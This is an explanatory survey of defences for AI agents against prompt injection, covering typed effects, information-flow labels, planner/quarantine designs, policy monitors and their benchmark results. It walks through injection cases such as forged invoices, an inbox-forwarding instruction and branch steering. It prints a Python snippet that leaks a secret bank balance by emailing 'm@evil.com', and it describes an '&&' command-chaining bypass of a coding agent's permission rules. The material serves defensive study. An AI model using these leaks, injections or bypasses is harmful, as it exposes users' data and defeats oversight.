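Zhou and colleagues' Language-Based Agent Control uses Haskell, whose types record effects. Any function that interacts with the outside world has the marker IO in its type, and so does any program that uses such a function. A developer who asks the agent for an Int, a whole number, therefore gets a program that can only calculate. Zhou and colleagues imagine a user asking a public calculator to delete every file on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. If the model writes a program that does both, the program has an IO type where the developer asked for Int, so the type checker rejects it.

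Most agents need some effects, so developers define narrower types than IO. Zhou and colleagues give the example of an agent that compiles bibliographies under a policy that every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. They define an effect type called BibIO with three operations, which search DBLP, fetch an entry and append an entry to a file. The agent has to return a program of type BibIO. The program can sort, filter and compare the results freely, but it can't call Haskell's general function for writing files, because that function belongs to IO.

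This alone would not stop the agent from inventing an entry and appending it. The append operation therefore accepts only values of type Trusted, and the library hides the constructor, the function that creates such values. The agent can get a Trusted entry only by fetching it from DBLP, so the type proves where the entry came from. The accounts assistant's list of suppliers could work the same way.

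A simpler design would give the agent a single tool that fetches an entry and appends it in one step. This would also enforce the policy, but the agent couldn't use code to compare entries before choosing one. To find the earliest paper on a subject, the model would have to read the entries itself.

Haskell also has features that bypass its type system. The best known is unsafePerformIO, which hides an effect inside a seemingly pure value. Safe Haskell, a subset of the language that developers can turn on with a compiler setting, removes these features, roughly as safe mode does for Scala.

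In ELBA, Zhou and colleagues' implementation (called TypeGuard in an earlier version), a call to an agent is an ordinary function call with an expected type. The model writes a program, and the type checker either accepts it or returns the error so the model can try again. The program may call further agents, for instance to read search results and decide what to do next. A sub-agent called inside a BibIO program must also return a BibIO program, so it has the same three operations as its parent. The parent can give it a stricter type, such as one with no effects, but cannot give it IO, so a hijacked agent cannot gain extra operations by delegating work.

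Zhou and colleagues tested the bibliography agent on 100 topics. None of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier, while an agent with a web search tool got 19 out of 1,002 wrong. The comparison slightly overstates the benefit of the types, because the second agent had no direct access to DBLP and wrote its citations from search results and memory. The policy also doesn't check whether a paper is relevant to the topic.

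### A simulated worst case

To protect against prompt injection, Zhou and colleagues combined ELBA with LIO, an established Haskell library that labels data with its sources. Under their policy, an agent that reads a web page drops to the trust level of the page's author and can no longer do anything the author would not be allowed to do. LIO checks the labels while the program runs, and the type system ensures that every effect goes through LIO.

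They used AgentDojo's simulated team chat, where all four models resisted all 105 attacks without any policy, under each of three wordings of the attacks. The unmodified test can therefore no longer show whether one design is more secure than another.

Zhou and colleagues simulated models that always obey planted attacks. In ELBA, sub-agents read all outside data, and each normally gets a task along with the text to work on. Whenever the text contained an attack, they removed the task and left the attacker's words as the only instruction. For each model, they ran the 105 combinations of task and attack seven times with policies and seven times without, for 735 runs in each condition.

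| Model | Attacks resisted with policies | Attacks resisted without | Tasks completed with policies | Tasks completed without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

The policies stopped every attack, even though the sub-agents were doing what the attacker wanted. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies as successful attacks, because the agent had opened a web address that the attacker supplied, but Zhou and colleagues checked all 29 by hand and found no violation. Their policy allows an agent to open a fixed address, but not to put private data into it or to act with full privileges on what the page contains.

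Agents completed 33% to 44% fewer tasks with the policies than without them, depending on the model. The policies also reduced the number of tasks completed when there were no attacks, from 14 to 18 of the 21 ordinary tasks down to 8 to 10. This was still about twice as many as CaMeL completed with its policies on, although ELBA took three times as long.

Very little of this loss comes from having to write typed Haskell. The agents wrote Haskell in both conditions, and the type checker rejected a program only about once in every eight runs. The tasks failed because the policy forbids some legitimate requests along with the attacks. If a user asks an agent to read a web page and do what it says, a policy against following instructions from web pages will block the request however well the agent writes its program. Zhou and colleagues suggest using such a policy as a filter when a person supervises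 the agent, so that actions that pass can go ahead without approval and the person only has to review the rest.

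## Separating plans from untrusted data and tracking its flow

TACIT and ELBA check programs written by a model that may already have read untrusted text. Developers can also have the model write its program before it reads any untrusted text, so that an attacker can't influence the plan. The programmer Simon Willison proposed a design for this, the dual-LLM pattern, in 2023. A privileged model reads the user's request, plans the work and can call tools, but it never sees the emails, files or web pages. A quarantined model reads those, but it has no tools and can only return an answer. The surrounding software stores the answer in a variable, which the privileged model refers to by name without seeing its contents.

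### What a fixed plan protects

Suppose a user asks the accounts assistant to pay the Acme invoice. The privileged model might write this plan:

```python
invoice = read_file("acme-invoice.txt")
bill = ask_quarantined("Find the account number and the amount", invoice)
send_money(bill.account, bill.amount)
```

If the invoice contains a hidden instruction to email the company's contracts to a stranger, the instruction has no effect, because the plan has no step that sends email and the quarantined model cannot add one. The plan also makes exactly one payment, whatever the invoice contains. This property, called control-flow integrity, means that only the planner determines which actions can run, in what order and under what conditions.

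But the account number still comes from the invoice, so an attacker who changes it gets the money even though every step ran as planned. Girrens and Wang (2026) point out in *SPA* that such an attack needs no hidden instruction, only a false value in the right place. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a milder case, in which an agent must email today's schedule to the user's boss. A poisoned calendar entry can corrupt the body of the email, but it can't change the recipient, because the address came from the user. The software can tell these cases apart only if it knows where each value came from.

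### Labels on values

An information-flow label is a tag that records how trustworthy or secret a value's sources are. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the simplest scheme, in which a value is either trusted or untrusted, and either public or secret. When the software computes a new value from several old ones, it gives the result the most restrictive combination of their labels, called the join and written ⊔. For example, a message that combines the user's words with text from an invoice is untrusted.

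Labels can also list people. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, let a label name everyone who may read a document. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one contract, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, then only Ben and Carla may read a comparison of the two:

**{Ana, Ben, Carla} ⊔ {Ben, Carla, Dev} = {Ben, Carla}**

A label for trustworthiness can list everyone who may have written a document. A text based on two documents gets a label that combines both lists. If each document's label lists two different people, the new label lists all four, since any of them could have influenced the text.

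Just before each tool call, the software checks the labels against a policy. One of Costa and colleagues' policies allows a consequential action, such as a payment, only if the decision to take it and all its arguments are trusted. Another allows a tool to send information only if every recipient is allowed to read it. In the Acme plan, `bill.account` is untrusted because it came from an untrusted file, so the first policy blocks the payment. A looser policy might check only the recipient. It would allow the payment if the plan took the account number from the company's own supplier list, but it would not catch an inflated amount on the invoice.

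### CaMeL

Google DeepMind's CaMeL (2025) combines the two-model pattern with labels. The privileged model writes a program in a subset of Python, and a custom interpreter runs it. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) explains that the interpreter tracks the origin of all data and checks a policy before each tool call. The labels, called capabilities, record a value's sources and who may receive it.

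The program can contain branches and loops, so untrusted data may affect which steps run. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) notes that such data can select a branch that the planner wrote but can't add a new one. The paper also found that the planner needs a full description of what each tool returns, because it has to write the code that processes a tool's output before the tool has run.

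Models write Python well, but its data flows are hard to track. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes this to Python's dynamic types, its reflection and its use of exceptions to change what runs next, and proposes a purpose-built language with bounded loops and simple conditionals. Girrens and Wang observe that each tool in CaMeL has its own policy, so the guarantee also depends on developers writing every policy correctly.

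### FIDES

A planner that must write its whole program in advance cannot adjust to unexpected results. In FIDES, Costa and colleagues' system, the planner works one step at a time and sees some of the tool results. The software keeps a label for the planner's whole conversation. When a tool returns something that would make this label more restrictive, the software hides it in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner might therefore see the date and amount of a bank transaction but not the subject line, which the sender wrote. The planner can open the variable, but the conversation then becomes untrusted and the policies block consequential actions.

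Some tasks depend on what the untrusted text says. A user might ask an agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, create a calendar event. In FIDES, the planner can ask the quarantined model whether the emails contain a request and use constrained decoding to limit the answer to yes or no. The answer's label also records its type, so a policy can allow an untrusted yes or no, which carries one bit of information, and still block untrusted text. If the answer is yes, the planner has the quarantined model put the meeting details in another variable, then passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading it.

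Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, but without these restricted answers, which few of the tasks needed. After removing misjudged cases, they counted 152 successful attacks against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES without policy checks, and none against FIDES with them. The ordinary agent completed 98.8% of the banking tasks without policy checks. With them, it completed 37.5% and FIDES completed 52.5%. In most of the failures they examined, FIDES was working as intended. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, and reading the file makes the conversation untrusted.

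According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), FIDES is now an experimental part of the company's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. When a tool call violates a policy, the software can ask the user to approve it. Any tool a developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public, so an omission can create a vulnerability without anyone noticing. Microsoft is considering a stricter default.

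### A leak through the branch not taken

Labels are easy to get wrong. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found several flaws in CaMeL's interpreter, one of which is a textbook example that dates back to 1974. Suppose a program tries to tell an outsider whether a customer's secret bank balance is above some threshold. If it sends an email inside the condition `if account.balance > threshold`, CaMeL blocks it, because the decision to send depends on a secret. But a program can get the same result in a roundabout way:

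```python
rich = True
low = True
if account.balance > threshold: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, the third line sets `low` to False, and CaMeL labels `low` secret. Because `low` is False, the program skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` stays True and public. The last line then sends the email without breaking any policy. When the balance is low, the fourth line sets `rich` to False and no email goes out. The outsider can therefore learn whether the balance is high from whether the email arrives. CaMeL doesn't prevent this because it raises a variable's label only in a branch that runs, and when the balance is high, the branch that assigns `rich` doesn't run.

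The standard remedy is to stop a program when it tries to change a public variable under a secret condition, which in this example happens in the third line. But stopping also reveals that the balance is high. Leaking a single bit matters little, and most systems of this kind tolerate it. But CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop that tries again after a failure, and nothing tracks what the failures reveal. A program could leak a whole secret one bit at a time by repeatedly failing on purpose.

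In CaMeL the attacker doesn't write the program, so these leaks require a faulty or hostile planner. They still matter, because safety by construction has to hold for such planners too. Another flaw could affect ordinary plans, because CaMeL's interpreter treats the result as trusted when a program inserts an untrusted value into a text template, a common way to compose a message.

FIDES deliberately omits this kind of tracking. Its labels follow data that a program copies or transforms, a property called explicit secrecy, but not information that an observer could infer from which tools the agent called. Costa and colleagues argue that full tracking would in effect forbid an agent from taking any publicly visible action after reading a secret.

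### Noninterference in LLMbda

Garby and colleagues instead propose LLMbda, a very small programming language for agents in which every value has a label. The conversation with the model is labeled with the join of its messages' labels. Any reply inherits the conversation's label, and so does everything computed by code in that reply. In a program, `fork` copies the conversation for a side task, `clear` empties it, and `assert` stops with an error if a value's label is too restrictive for some use. To make a quarantined reader, a program forks the conversation, clears the copy and asks its question there. Programmers can therefore write the two-model pattern themselves in LLMbda, whereas CaMeL and FIDES have it built in.

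LLMbda guarantees noninterference, the property that untrusted inputs cannot influence trusted outputs and secret inputs cannot influence public ones. Imagine two runs of the accounts assistant that differ only in the text of an untrusted invoice. Everything labelled trusted at the end must then be the same in both. Write x ~ y when two inputs or outputs agree on everything labelled trusted. If a program p involves no chance and finishes on both inputs, the condition is

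**x ~ y implies p(x) ~ p(y).**

Language models do involve chance, and a program may also run forever or stop at a failed check. Let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities that the two runs finish with the trusted result q. Garby and colleagues require that some third set of probabilities ω covers both:

**μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, with Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.**

Suppose that with one invoice the assistant pays Acme with probability 0.6, pays nobody with probability 0.3, and fails to finish with probability 0.1. With the other invoice, the probabilities are 0.7, 0.2 and 0.1. Then ω can be 0.7 for paying Acme and 0.3 for paying nobody, which add up to 1, so the condition holds. If the second invoice raised the chance of paying Acme to 0.9, ω would have to be at least 0.9 for paying Acme and 0.3 for paying nobody. These add up to 1.2, so the program would violate noninterference. The condition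 limits the difference between the two runs to their average chance of not finishing, so for programs that always finish, the probabilities must be identical.

Garby and colleagues prove that every LLMbda program meets this condition by defining a second set of rules for running programs. These rules replace a computation with a dummy value as soon as its label shows that it depends on something the observer may not see. Under these rules, two inputs that look alike to the observer give exactly the same probabilities, which serve as ω. The theorem also covers programs that a model writes during the run and assumes nothing about what the model writes.

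Garby and colleagues wrote their interpreter in Lean, which can run programs as well as check proofs. Their theorems cover the interpreter that calls the model, whereas the proofs about Scala's capture checking cover only simplified versions of the language. The trusted base still includes Lean, the code that contacts the model over the network, and the labels and checks that developers attach to tools. The theory treats every data source as part of the program, so it does not fully describe outside services.

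### Endorsement

Strict noninterference would make many agents useless, because users often want an agent to act on something it has read. LLMbda therefore has an `endorse` operation that relabels an untrusted value as trusted. In Garby and colleagues' example, an agent acknowledges incoming emails and puts a category, such as "general", in each reply's subject line. The quarantined model picks the category from a fixed list, and the program endorses that choice. An attacker can influence which category appears but cannot insert any other text. With eight categories, the attacker controls at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits.

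A reviewer can find every exception a program makes by searching for `endorse`, whereas exceptions are harder to find when they are gaps in the tracking. Garby and colleagues prove that secrets still can't influence public outputs, whatever untrusted inputs the attacker chooses and whatever the program endorses. But `endorse` has no built-in limit, so a careless planner could endorse an entire web page. Garby and colleagues describe optional restrictions, such as allowing only a small set of possible values.

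### A verified agent in a simulated bank

Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in LLMbda. Agents often need several attempts to write working code, and the error message from a failed attempt may contain untrusted text. In LLMbda, that text would make the next plan untrusted too, so the plan could no longer make payments. Randori avoids this by having the model write and repair its plan using an invented bank account, then running only the finished plan on the real one. The model also decides what to endorse while it writes the plan, before it has seen any outside data.

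Randori and CaMeL were each run three times on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. The table shows how many of each system's 48 runs without attacks succeeded.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 36 | 36 | 31 |
| Randori without endorsement | – | 30 | 26 |
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 | – | 34 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 | – | 18 |

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* describes CaMeL's task performance as comparable to that of other defences, but in this test its policies cut the number of completed tasks by almost half. Randori completed about as many tasks with its checks on as CaMeL did with its policies off. With only 16 different tasks, the margins of error are 19 to 27 percentage points, too large to tell which of those two is better. Randori's advantage over CaMeL with policies on comes partly from endorsement, and may also come partly from enforcing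 only a subset of CaMeL's policies.

Randori resisted the attack in all but 2 of 1,296 runs. Two-thirds of these runs were easy to resist, because the attack needed a tool that the plan would never have called. Both successful attacks were among the other 423 runs. In the same group of harder attacks, CaMeL with its policies off resisted the attack in all 141 runs with GPT-5.2 and in 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. On this benchmark, fixing the plan in advance provides most of the protection, and labels can prevent only a few more attacks.

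### When the user tells the agent to obey a document

Both successful attacks on Randori exploited the same task. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a malicious payment request. The plan endorsed whatever the file contained, so the attacker received the payment.

Labels cannot solve this problem, because they record where a text came from, not whether what it says is true. A genuine bill and a forged one are both files that an outsider could have written, so they get the same label. A policy based on labels must therefore allow both or block both. When Garby and colleagues removed endorsement from Randori, they blocked the attack but also stopped the agent from paying genuine bills this way.

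Other systems have the same difficulty. CaMeL's designers found the same case in their tests and placed it outside the attacks they aim to stop. When Girrens and Wang switched off label checks in their system, only four of 949 attacks succeeded, all by exploiting a single banking task in which the agent reads a file and follows its instructions. Garby and colleagues say that four independent systems, including TACIT and FIDES, were left with the same cases. That somewhat overstates the agreement, since TACIT's only failure was the hotel review described earlier, and FIDES's matching case was also a quoted review. The argument follows from what labels record, so it doesn't depend on how many systems share the difficulty.

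Developers can still limit how much a document influences an agent's actions. If the accounts assistant may pay only suppliers on the company's list, a forged bill can at worst cause it to pay the wrong listed supplier or the wrong amount. The software can also ask the user to confirm the payment. Costa and colleagues note that mail servers can authenticate a sender's address, so an agent could treat the address as trusted even when the message isn't. These measures don't help much with a request such as "read this file and do what it says", because the user is letting whoever wrote the file choose the action.

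### Agents that use a screen

Many agents operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. A planner that never sees the screen has to anticipate everything that might appear on it. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner write one large program with a branch for each likely situation. For example, the program might use a quarantined vision model to check for a cookie banner, and close the banner if there is one. These plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five tool calls and four branches for AgentDojo tasks.

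Foerster and colleagues report that the design kept up to 57% of a leading model's performance. The figure comes from 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed without the protection. With it, the agent completed 31 of them on the first attempt and 62, or 57%, in at least one of five attempts. In practice, something would have to identify the successful attempt. The protected agent used 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected one. A version based on FIDES, which calls the planner again at every step, used 29.6 times as many.

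Policies on tool calls are hard to apply to agents that click on a screen, because a click at certain coordinates may log the user in, delete a file or open a malicious site. An attacker can also steer the agent down a branch that its plan already contains, an attack Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. They made an advertisement look like a cookie banner, and the agent clicked on it because its plan included closing such banners. They tried comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code and consulting a second model, but neither check reliably stopped these attacks.

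### Agents that remember

When an agent keeps information between requests, an attack hidden in data from one request can affect a later one. In Girrens and Wang's example, a user asks an agent on Monday to fetch an Acme invoice and remember the details, and on Tuesday asks it to pay. If Tuesday's planner reads the stored text, a hidden instruction in it can change the new plan. Their system, SPA, stores each result with its label and shows later planners only a description of the result. The program retrieves the actual value when it runs, and the value keeps its original label.

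SPA's planner writes in a language with six kinds of step: retrieving a stored result, calling a tool, querying the quarantined model, showing something to the user, branching, and looping. A plan cannot do arithmetic or fill in text templates. Because the language is small, a checker can follow the labels through both sides of every branch before anything runs. A variable created inside a branch disappears when the branch ends, which rules out the roundabout email about the bank balance. If the checker rejects a plan, SPA stops instead of asking for another, so an attacker can't learn from repeated rejections or use them to steer the planner.

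With label checks on, no attacks succeeded on AgentDojo, and 0.2% succeeded on a version that spreads each task over several requests. But the share of tasks completed fell from 53.0% to 29.0% on the original and from 62.5% to 35.3% on the multi-request version. Attacks succeeded in at most 0.4% of runs even without the checks, so these results are clearer evidence that the checks reduce task completion than that they prevent attacks. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that the attacks they used seldom test whether stored text can do harm later.

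### Agents that call other agents

When one agent gives work to another, the second treats the first as its user. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a team of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked it to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. The applicant database contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The agent that read the database and the agent in charge both kept this text in variables, where their planners couldn't see it. But the agent in charge put the summary into its request to the messaging agent. That agent's planner read the request as trusted instructions and added the email to the outside address to its plan.

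Multi-CaMeL splits each request into an instruction that may not depend on any tool's output and a set of variables that the receiving planner cannot see. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. On a set of industrial maintenance tasks, putting CaMeL in each agent lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL's separate channel for data lowered it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, these two losses averaged 13.4 and 0.85 points.

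Most of the failed tasks needed a step that became apparent only after a tool returned its result, when the plan could no longer change. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran all these tests without policies on data, so they measured only how much locking the plans in advance reduced task completion. An attacker could still have changed an account number inside a valid plan, and policies to prevent that would probably have blocked some legitimate tasks as well.

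## Rules checked while the system acts

CaMeL, FIDES and LLMbda each require developers to build the agent in a particular way. A company that already has a working agent can instead add a monitor, a program that sits between the agent and its tools and checks each action against a list of rules before allowing it. The check that stopped the streaming-service payment in *NOMOS* worked this way. The rules are written in a policy language, a small language for describing which actions to allow. Only the rule writers have to work within that language's restrictions, so developers can build the agent in any language.

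### One payment rule

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to transfer $100 to Bob. Bob is the user's son, but a friend or a new colleague might have the same name. Their rule is:

```
rule @inspect_transfer
trigger Transfer
check !is_to_family_member
enforce user_inspection
end
```

The trigger is the event that activates the rule, here an attempted transfer. The check is a condition (the exclamation mark means "not"). The last part is what the monitor does if the condition holds.

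If the agent tries to pay the son, the condition is false and the transfer goes through. If it tries to pay a colleague called Bob, the condition is true, so the monitor holds the transfer and shows it to the user. If the user approves, the transfer goes ahead, and if the user refuses, the monitor ends the task. With `stop` in place of `user_inspection`, the monitor would block every transfer outside the family without consulting the user. AgentSpec can also run an action that the developer chose in advance, such as slowing a car down, or prompt the language model for a new plan, which again relies on the model's judgement.

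The condition `is_to_family_member` is an ordinary Python function that somebody has to write, and it is part of the trusted base. If it compares only first names, it will accept a stranger who is also named Bob. AgentSpec also allows any action that no rule mentions, so an agent can buy Bob a gift card without triggering the rule.

### How AgentSpec performed

Wang and colleagues first tested an agent that writes and runs Python. They used RedCode-Exec, a set of 750 risky instructions in 25 categories, such as copying sensitive files, and wrote one rule per category. The agent tried to run code for 422 of the instructions, and the rules flagged 333 of those programs (79%). Wang and colleagues report a detection rate of over 90%, but their figures support this only if two categories are excluded because the agent's code turned out not to contain the requested flaw. They judged 58 of the flagged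 programs harmless and let them run. Because they wrote the rules from descriptions of the same 25 risks, the test is weak evidence of how well the rules would catch risks that nobody has listed.

In a second test, a household robot received dangerous instructions, such as pouring water onto a laptop. Without rules it carried out up to 79% of them, depending on the type of hazard, and with rules it carried out none. One rule, which lets the robot pour liquid only onto things on an approved list, covered 96 of the 250 dangerous cases. With rules, the robot completed 54.3% of safe tasks, down from 58.6%. In a third test, rules kept a self-driving system within the law in all eight scenarios where it had previously broken a traffic law, crashed or got stuck. Checking a rule's conditions took less than three milliseconds on average, while the coding agent's runs took about 25 seconds.

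Wang and colleagues also had OpenAI's o1 model write the rules. For the robot, these rules stopped only 71% of the dangerous actions, though about 96% of the actions they stopped were dangerous. When told to prevent harmful pouring, o1 banned all pouring, which would stop the robot from watering a plant. When asked to protect important configuration files, it tended to cover only the files in its examples. Current models would probably do better than o1, which is two years old, but they will still have to guess what a vague requirement covers.

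### Permissions that shrink

A fixed set of rules does not suit every task. Sending email is fine if the user asked for it, but suspicious if the user asked for a summary of the inbox. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) therefore has a language model write a new policy for each request. Each policy lists rules that allow or forbid a tool when its arguments meet certain conditions. The monitor applies the forbidding rules first and, unlike AgentSpec, blocks any call that no rule covers. When the monitor blocks a call, the agent by default gets an error message and carries on with the task, but developers can have the monitor end the run or ask the user instead.

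Suppose a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks listed in an email. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The tasks require sending a summary of recent emails over Slack, a team chat service, so the model proposes a wider policy that also allows reading emails and sending Slack messages. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, `alice`, the model narrows the policy to allow messages only to `alice`. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. The agent obeys it and calls `send_email`, but the monitor blocks the call because no rule allows that tool.

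An attacker might also try to fool the model that updates the policy. Progent therefore passes every update to an SMT solver, a program that works out whether a logical formula can be true. Write A(P) for the set of tool calls that a policy P allows. For an old policy P and a proposed policy P′, the solver checks whether

**A(P′) ⊆ A(P).**

If an update adds no permissions, it takes effect at once. Otherwise it needs approval, either from a person or through a setting the user chose earlier. Shi and colleagues call this guarantee monotonic confinement, because the set of allowed calls never grows without approval.

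The guarantee does not ensure that the policy keeps the right permissions. In the example, the wider policy allows Slack messages to anyone until the next update. If an attacker got the model to narrow the recipient to a stranger instead of `alice`, the solver would accept the change because it is also a reduction. Safety therefore depends heavily on how broad an expansion the user approves.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, another prompt-injection benchmark, the success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agents completed about as many tasks as before. In these runs the software approved every expansion automatically, to represent a careless user. The results therefore mostly reflect how well a model writes policies and hardly test the solver's guarantee. The model writes the first policy before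 the agent reads any untrusted text, and that policy alone cut successful attacks on AgentDojo to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer had few decisions to make.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that people make mistakes when they write such policies by hand, and that automatic updates rely on the model to filter out malicious instructions. The solver addresses the second problem only if somebody reviews the expansions. Progent also cannot stop an attack that uses only permitted calls. For example, a web page could persuade a shopping agent to choose the attacker's product from several valid ones.

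### Analysing Cedar policies in advance

Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues (2024), in *Cedar*, describe a policy language that Amazon Web Services uses to control access to its products. They designed it for ordinary software, but an agent's tool call is also a request by somebody to do something to a resource. The company with the accounts assistant might write two policies:

```
permit(
  principal == Agent::"accounts",
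  action == Action::"pay",
  resource)
when { resource is Supplier && context.amount <= 1000 };

forbid(
  principal,
  action == Action::"pay",
  resource)
when { resource.suspended };
```

A payment of 400 to an active supplier matches the first policy and goes through. Cedar denies a payment of 4,000 because no policy permits it. A payment of 400 to a suspended supplier matches both policies, and Cedar denies it because `forbid` always overrides `permit`. Cedar only returns allow or deny, so the company has to build its own step if it wants the assistant to ask a manager about the larger payment.

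A company with hundreds of policies needs to know their combined effect. In Cutler and colleagues' example, a to-do list application forbids interns to create lists. Somebody rewrites the policies, and the new version accidentally also stops interns from seeing which lists they own. Cedar's analyser translates both versions into logical formulas and uses an SMT solver to search for a request that only one of them allows. It finds a request from a particular intern that the old policies allow and the new ones deny. The search covers every possible request, so nobody has to anticipate the mistake and write a test case for it.

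Cedar can do this because its language is restricted. Policies have no side effects or general loops, so evaluating them always finishes, and their order makes no difference. Each policy also refers to a limited number of people, groups and resources, which the analyser can collect from the policy's text. This limit matters when groups contain other groups, because the analysis must rule out cases where group A is inside group B and B is inside A. Otherwise it will report problems that can't occur. Ruling out such circles among all possible groups would take formulas that a solver may never finish checking. Cedar's analyser rules them out only among the groups that the policy refers to, and Cutler and colleagues prove that this is enough. The analysis therefore misses no differences, reports no false ones, and uses only formulas that a solver can in principle always decide.

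Rego, a popular alternative, lets people write more complicated rules. It is based on Datalog, a language for which no procedure can decide in every case whether two programs are equivalent.

Cutler and colleagues compared the speed of Cedar, Rego and a third language, OpenFGA, by writing policies in each for three applications (file sharing, code hosting and to-do lists). They timed 100,000 random requests for each combination of application and amount of data. Cedar was 29 to 35 times as fast as OpenFGA and 43 to 81 times as fast as Rego. Checking a rewritten set of policies took 75 milliseconds on average. They also modelled Cedar in Lean and proved that it denies any request that no policy permits. Comparing the production code with the model on random inputs exposed nearly two dozen bugs. None of these tests involved an AI agent or an attack. They are good evidence that Cedar applies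 policies quickly and correctly, but the company still has to choose policies that stop the harm.

Cedar ignores any policy that causes an error during evaluation, according to *How We Built Cedar* (2024). If a supplier's record had no `suspended` field, the second policy above would cause an error, Cedar would apply only the first, and the payment would go out. Cedar comes with a validator that finds such mistakes beforehand if developers run it.

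### What a monitor can enforce

The year before his paper with Morrisett and Harper, Fred Schneider worked out the limits of monitors in general. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), considered monitors that see the steps of a single run and can only halt it. He proved that they can enforce nothing except safety properties. In this technical sense, a safety property is a rule that some bad thing never happens, where every run that breaks the rule does so at a definite point. If G is the set of acceptable runs, then for every run σ outside G there must be a number i such that

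**every run that begins with the first i steps of σ is also outside G.**

"Never pay the same invoice twice" is a safety property. A run breaks the rule at the second payment, and nothing the assistant does afterward can undo the violation. Schneider's proof relies on the fact that a monitor has no access to future steps. If the steps so far are unacceptable, the monitor has to halt the run even if later steps might correct the problem, because the program could stop at that moment. The monitor also has to halt a bad run after finitely many steps, or it will never halt it.

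The rule "the Acme invoice eventually gets paid" is not a safety property. However long the assistant has delayed, it might pay at the next step, so no finite part of the run shows a violation. Halting the assistant would leave the invoice unpaid. Setting a deadline of 50 steps turns the rule into a safety property, but a monitor can enforce it only by halting the assistant before the deadline passes. If the deadline is in seconds, the monitor can't enforce it even by halting the assistant, because time continues to pass.

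Noninterference is also not a safety property, because it compares runs. If an assistant might make any payment at all, whatever the invoice says, an observer can't learn anything about the invoice from its payments. But if some of the possible runs are removed so that the remaining payments depend on the invoice's text, the smaller set of runs violates noninterference even though the larger set satisfied it. A halting monitor can only remove runs, and removing runs can never break a safety property.

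Monitors can still prevent leaks by enforcing a stricter rule that is a safety property. Schneider's example is a ban on sending any message after reading a file. The monitor only has to track whether the program has read one, but the ban also blocks harmless messages, much as information-flow labels do. The theorem still applies when a monitor returns error messages, as Progent does. Schneider notes that notifying the program instead of halting it does not let a monitor enforce any more policies. Notification does let an agent finish the rest of its work.

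### Monitors that edit actions

In *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005), Ligatti, Bauer and Walker showed that a monitor can enforce more policies if it can suppress a program's actions and insert others. Such a monitor can hold actions back, let the program continue as if they had succeeded, and release them once they form an acceptable sequence, as a database does with a transaction.

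Suppose the company requires an entry in its audit log for every payment, and the assistant normally writes the entry after paying. This rule is not a safety property, because a later entry repairs the violation. A halting monitor would have to stop the payment, but an editing monitor can hold it and release both the payment and the entry only after the assistant writes the entry.

This works only for actions that the monitor can fake. Ligatti and colleagues point out that if a program needs the reply to an email before it can continue, the monitor has to let the email go out and can't take it back afterwards. Editing also doesn't help with noninterference, because the monitor still observes only one run. The audit rule is enforceable partly because an assistant that does nothing satisfies it. To guarantee that the Acme invoice gets paid, by contrast, the monitor would have to be able to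 pay it.

### Matching the text of commands

Schneider's ban on sending messages works only if the monitor recognises every way to send one, and he warned that some of these might be buried deep in the system. A call to a tool such as pay(supplier, amount) is easy to recognise because its name and arguments determine what it does. But coding agents do much of their work through shell commands, which are lines of text for the operating system, and many different commands can have the same effect.

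Many coding agents match shell commands against patterns. In Anthropic's Claude Code, for example, a rule consists of a tool's name and a pattern in brackets, so `Bash(*)` covers every shell command. Zhou and colleagues report that in March 2026 a fault in Claude Code let forbidden commands through when they followed another command and `&&`, because the software compared only the first command with its list.

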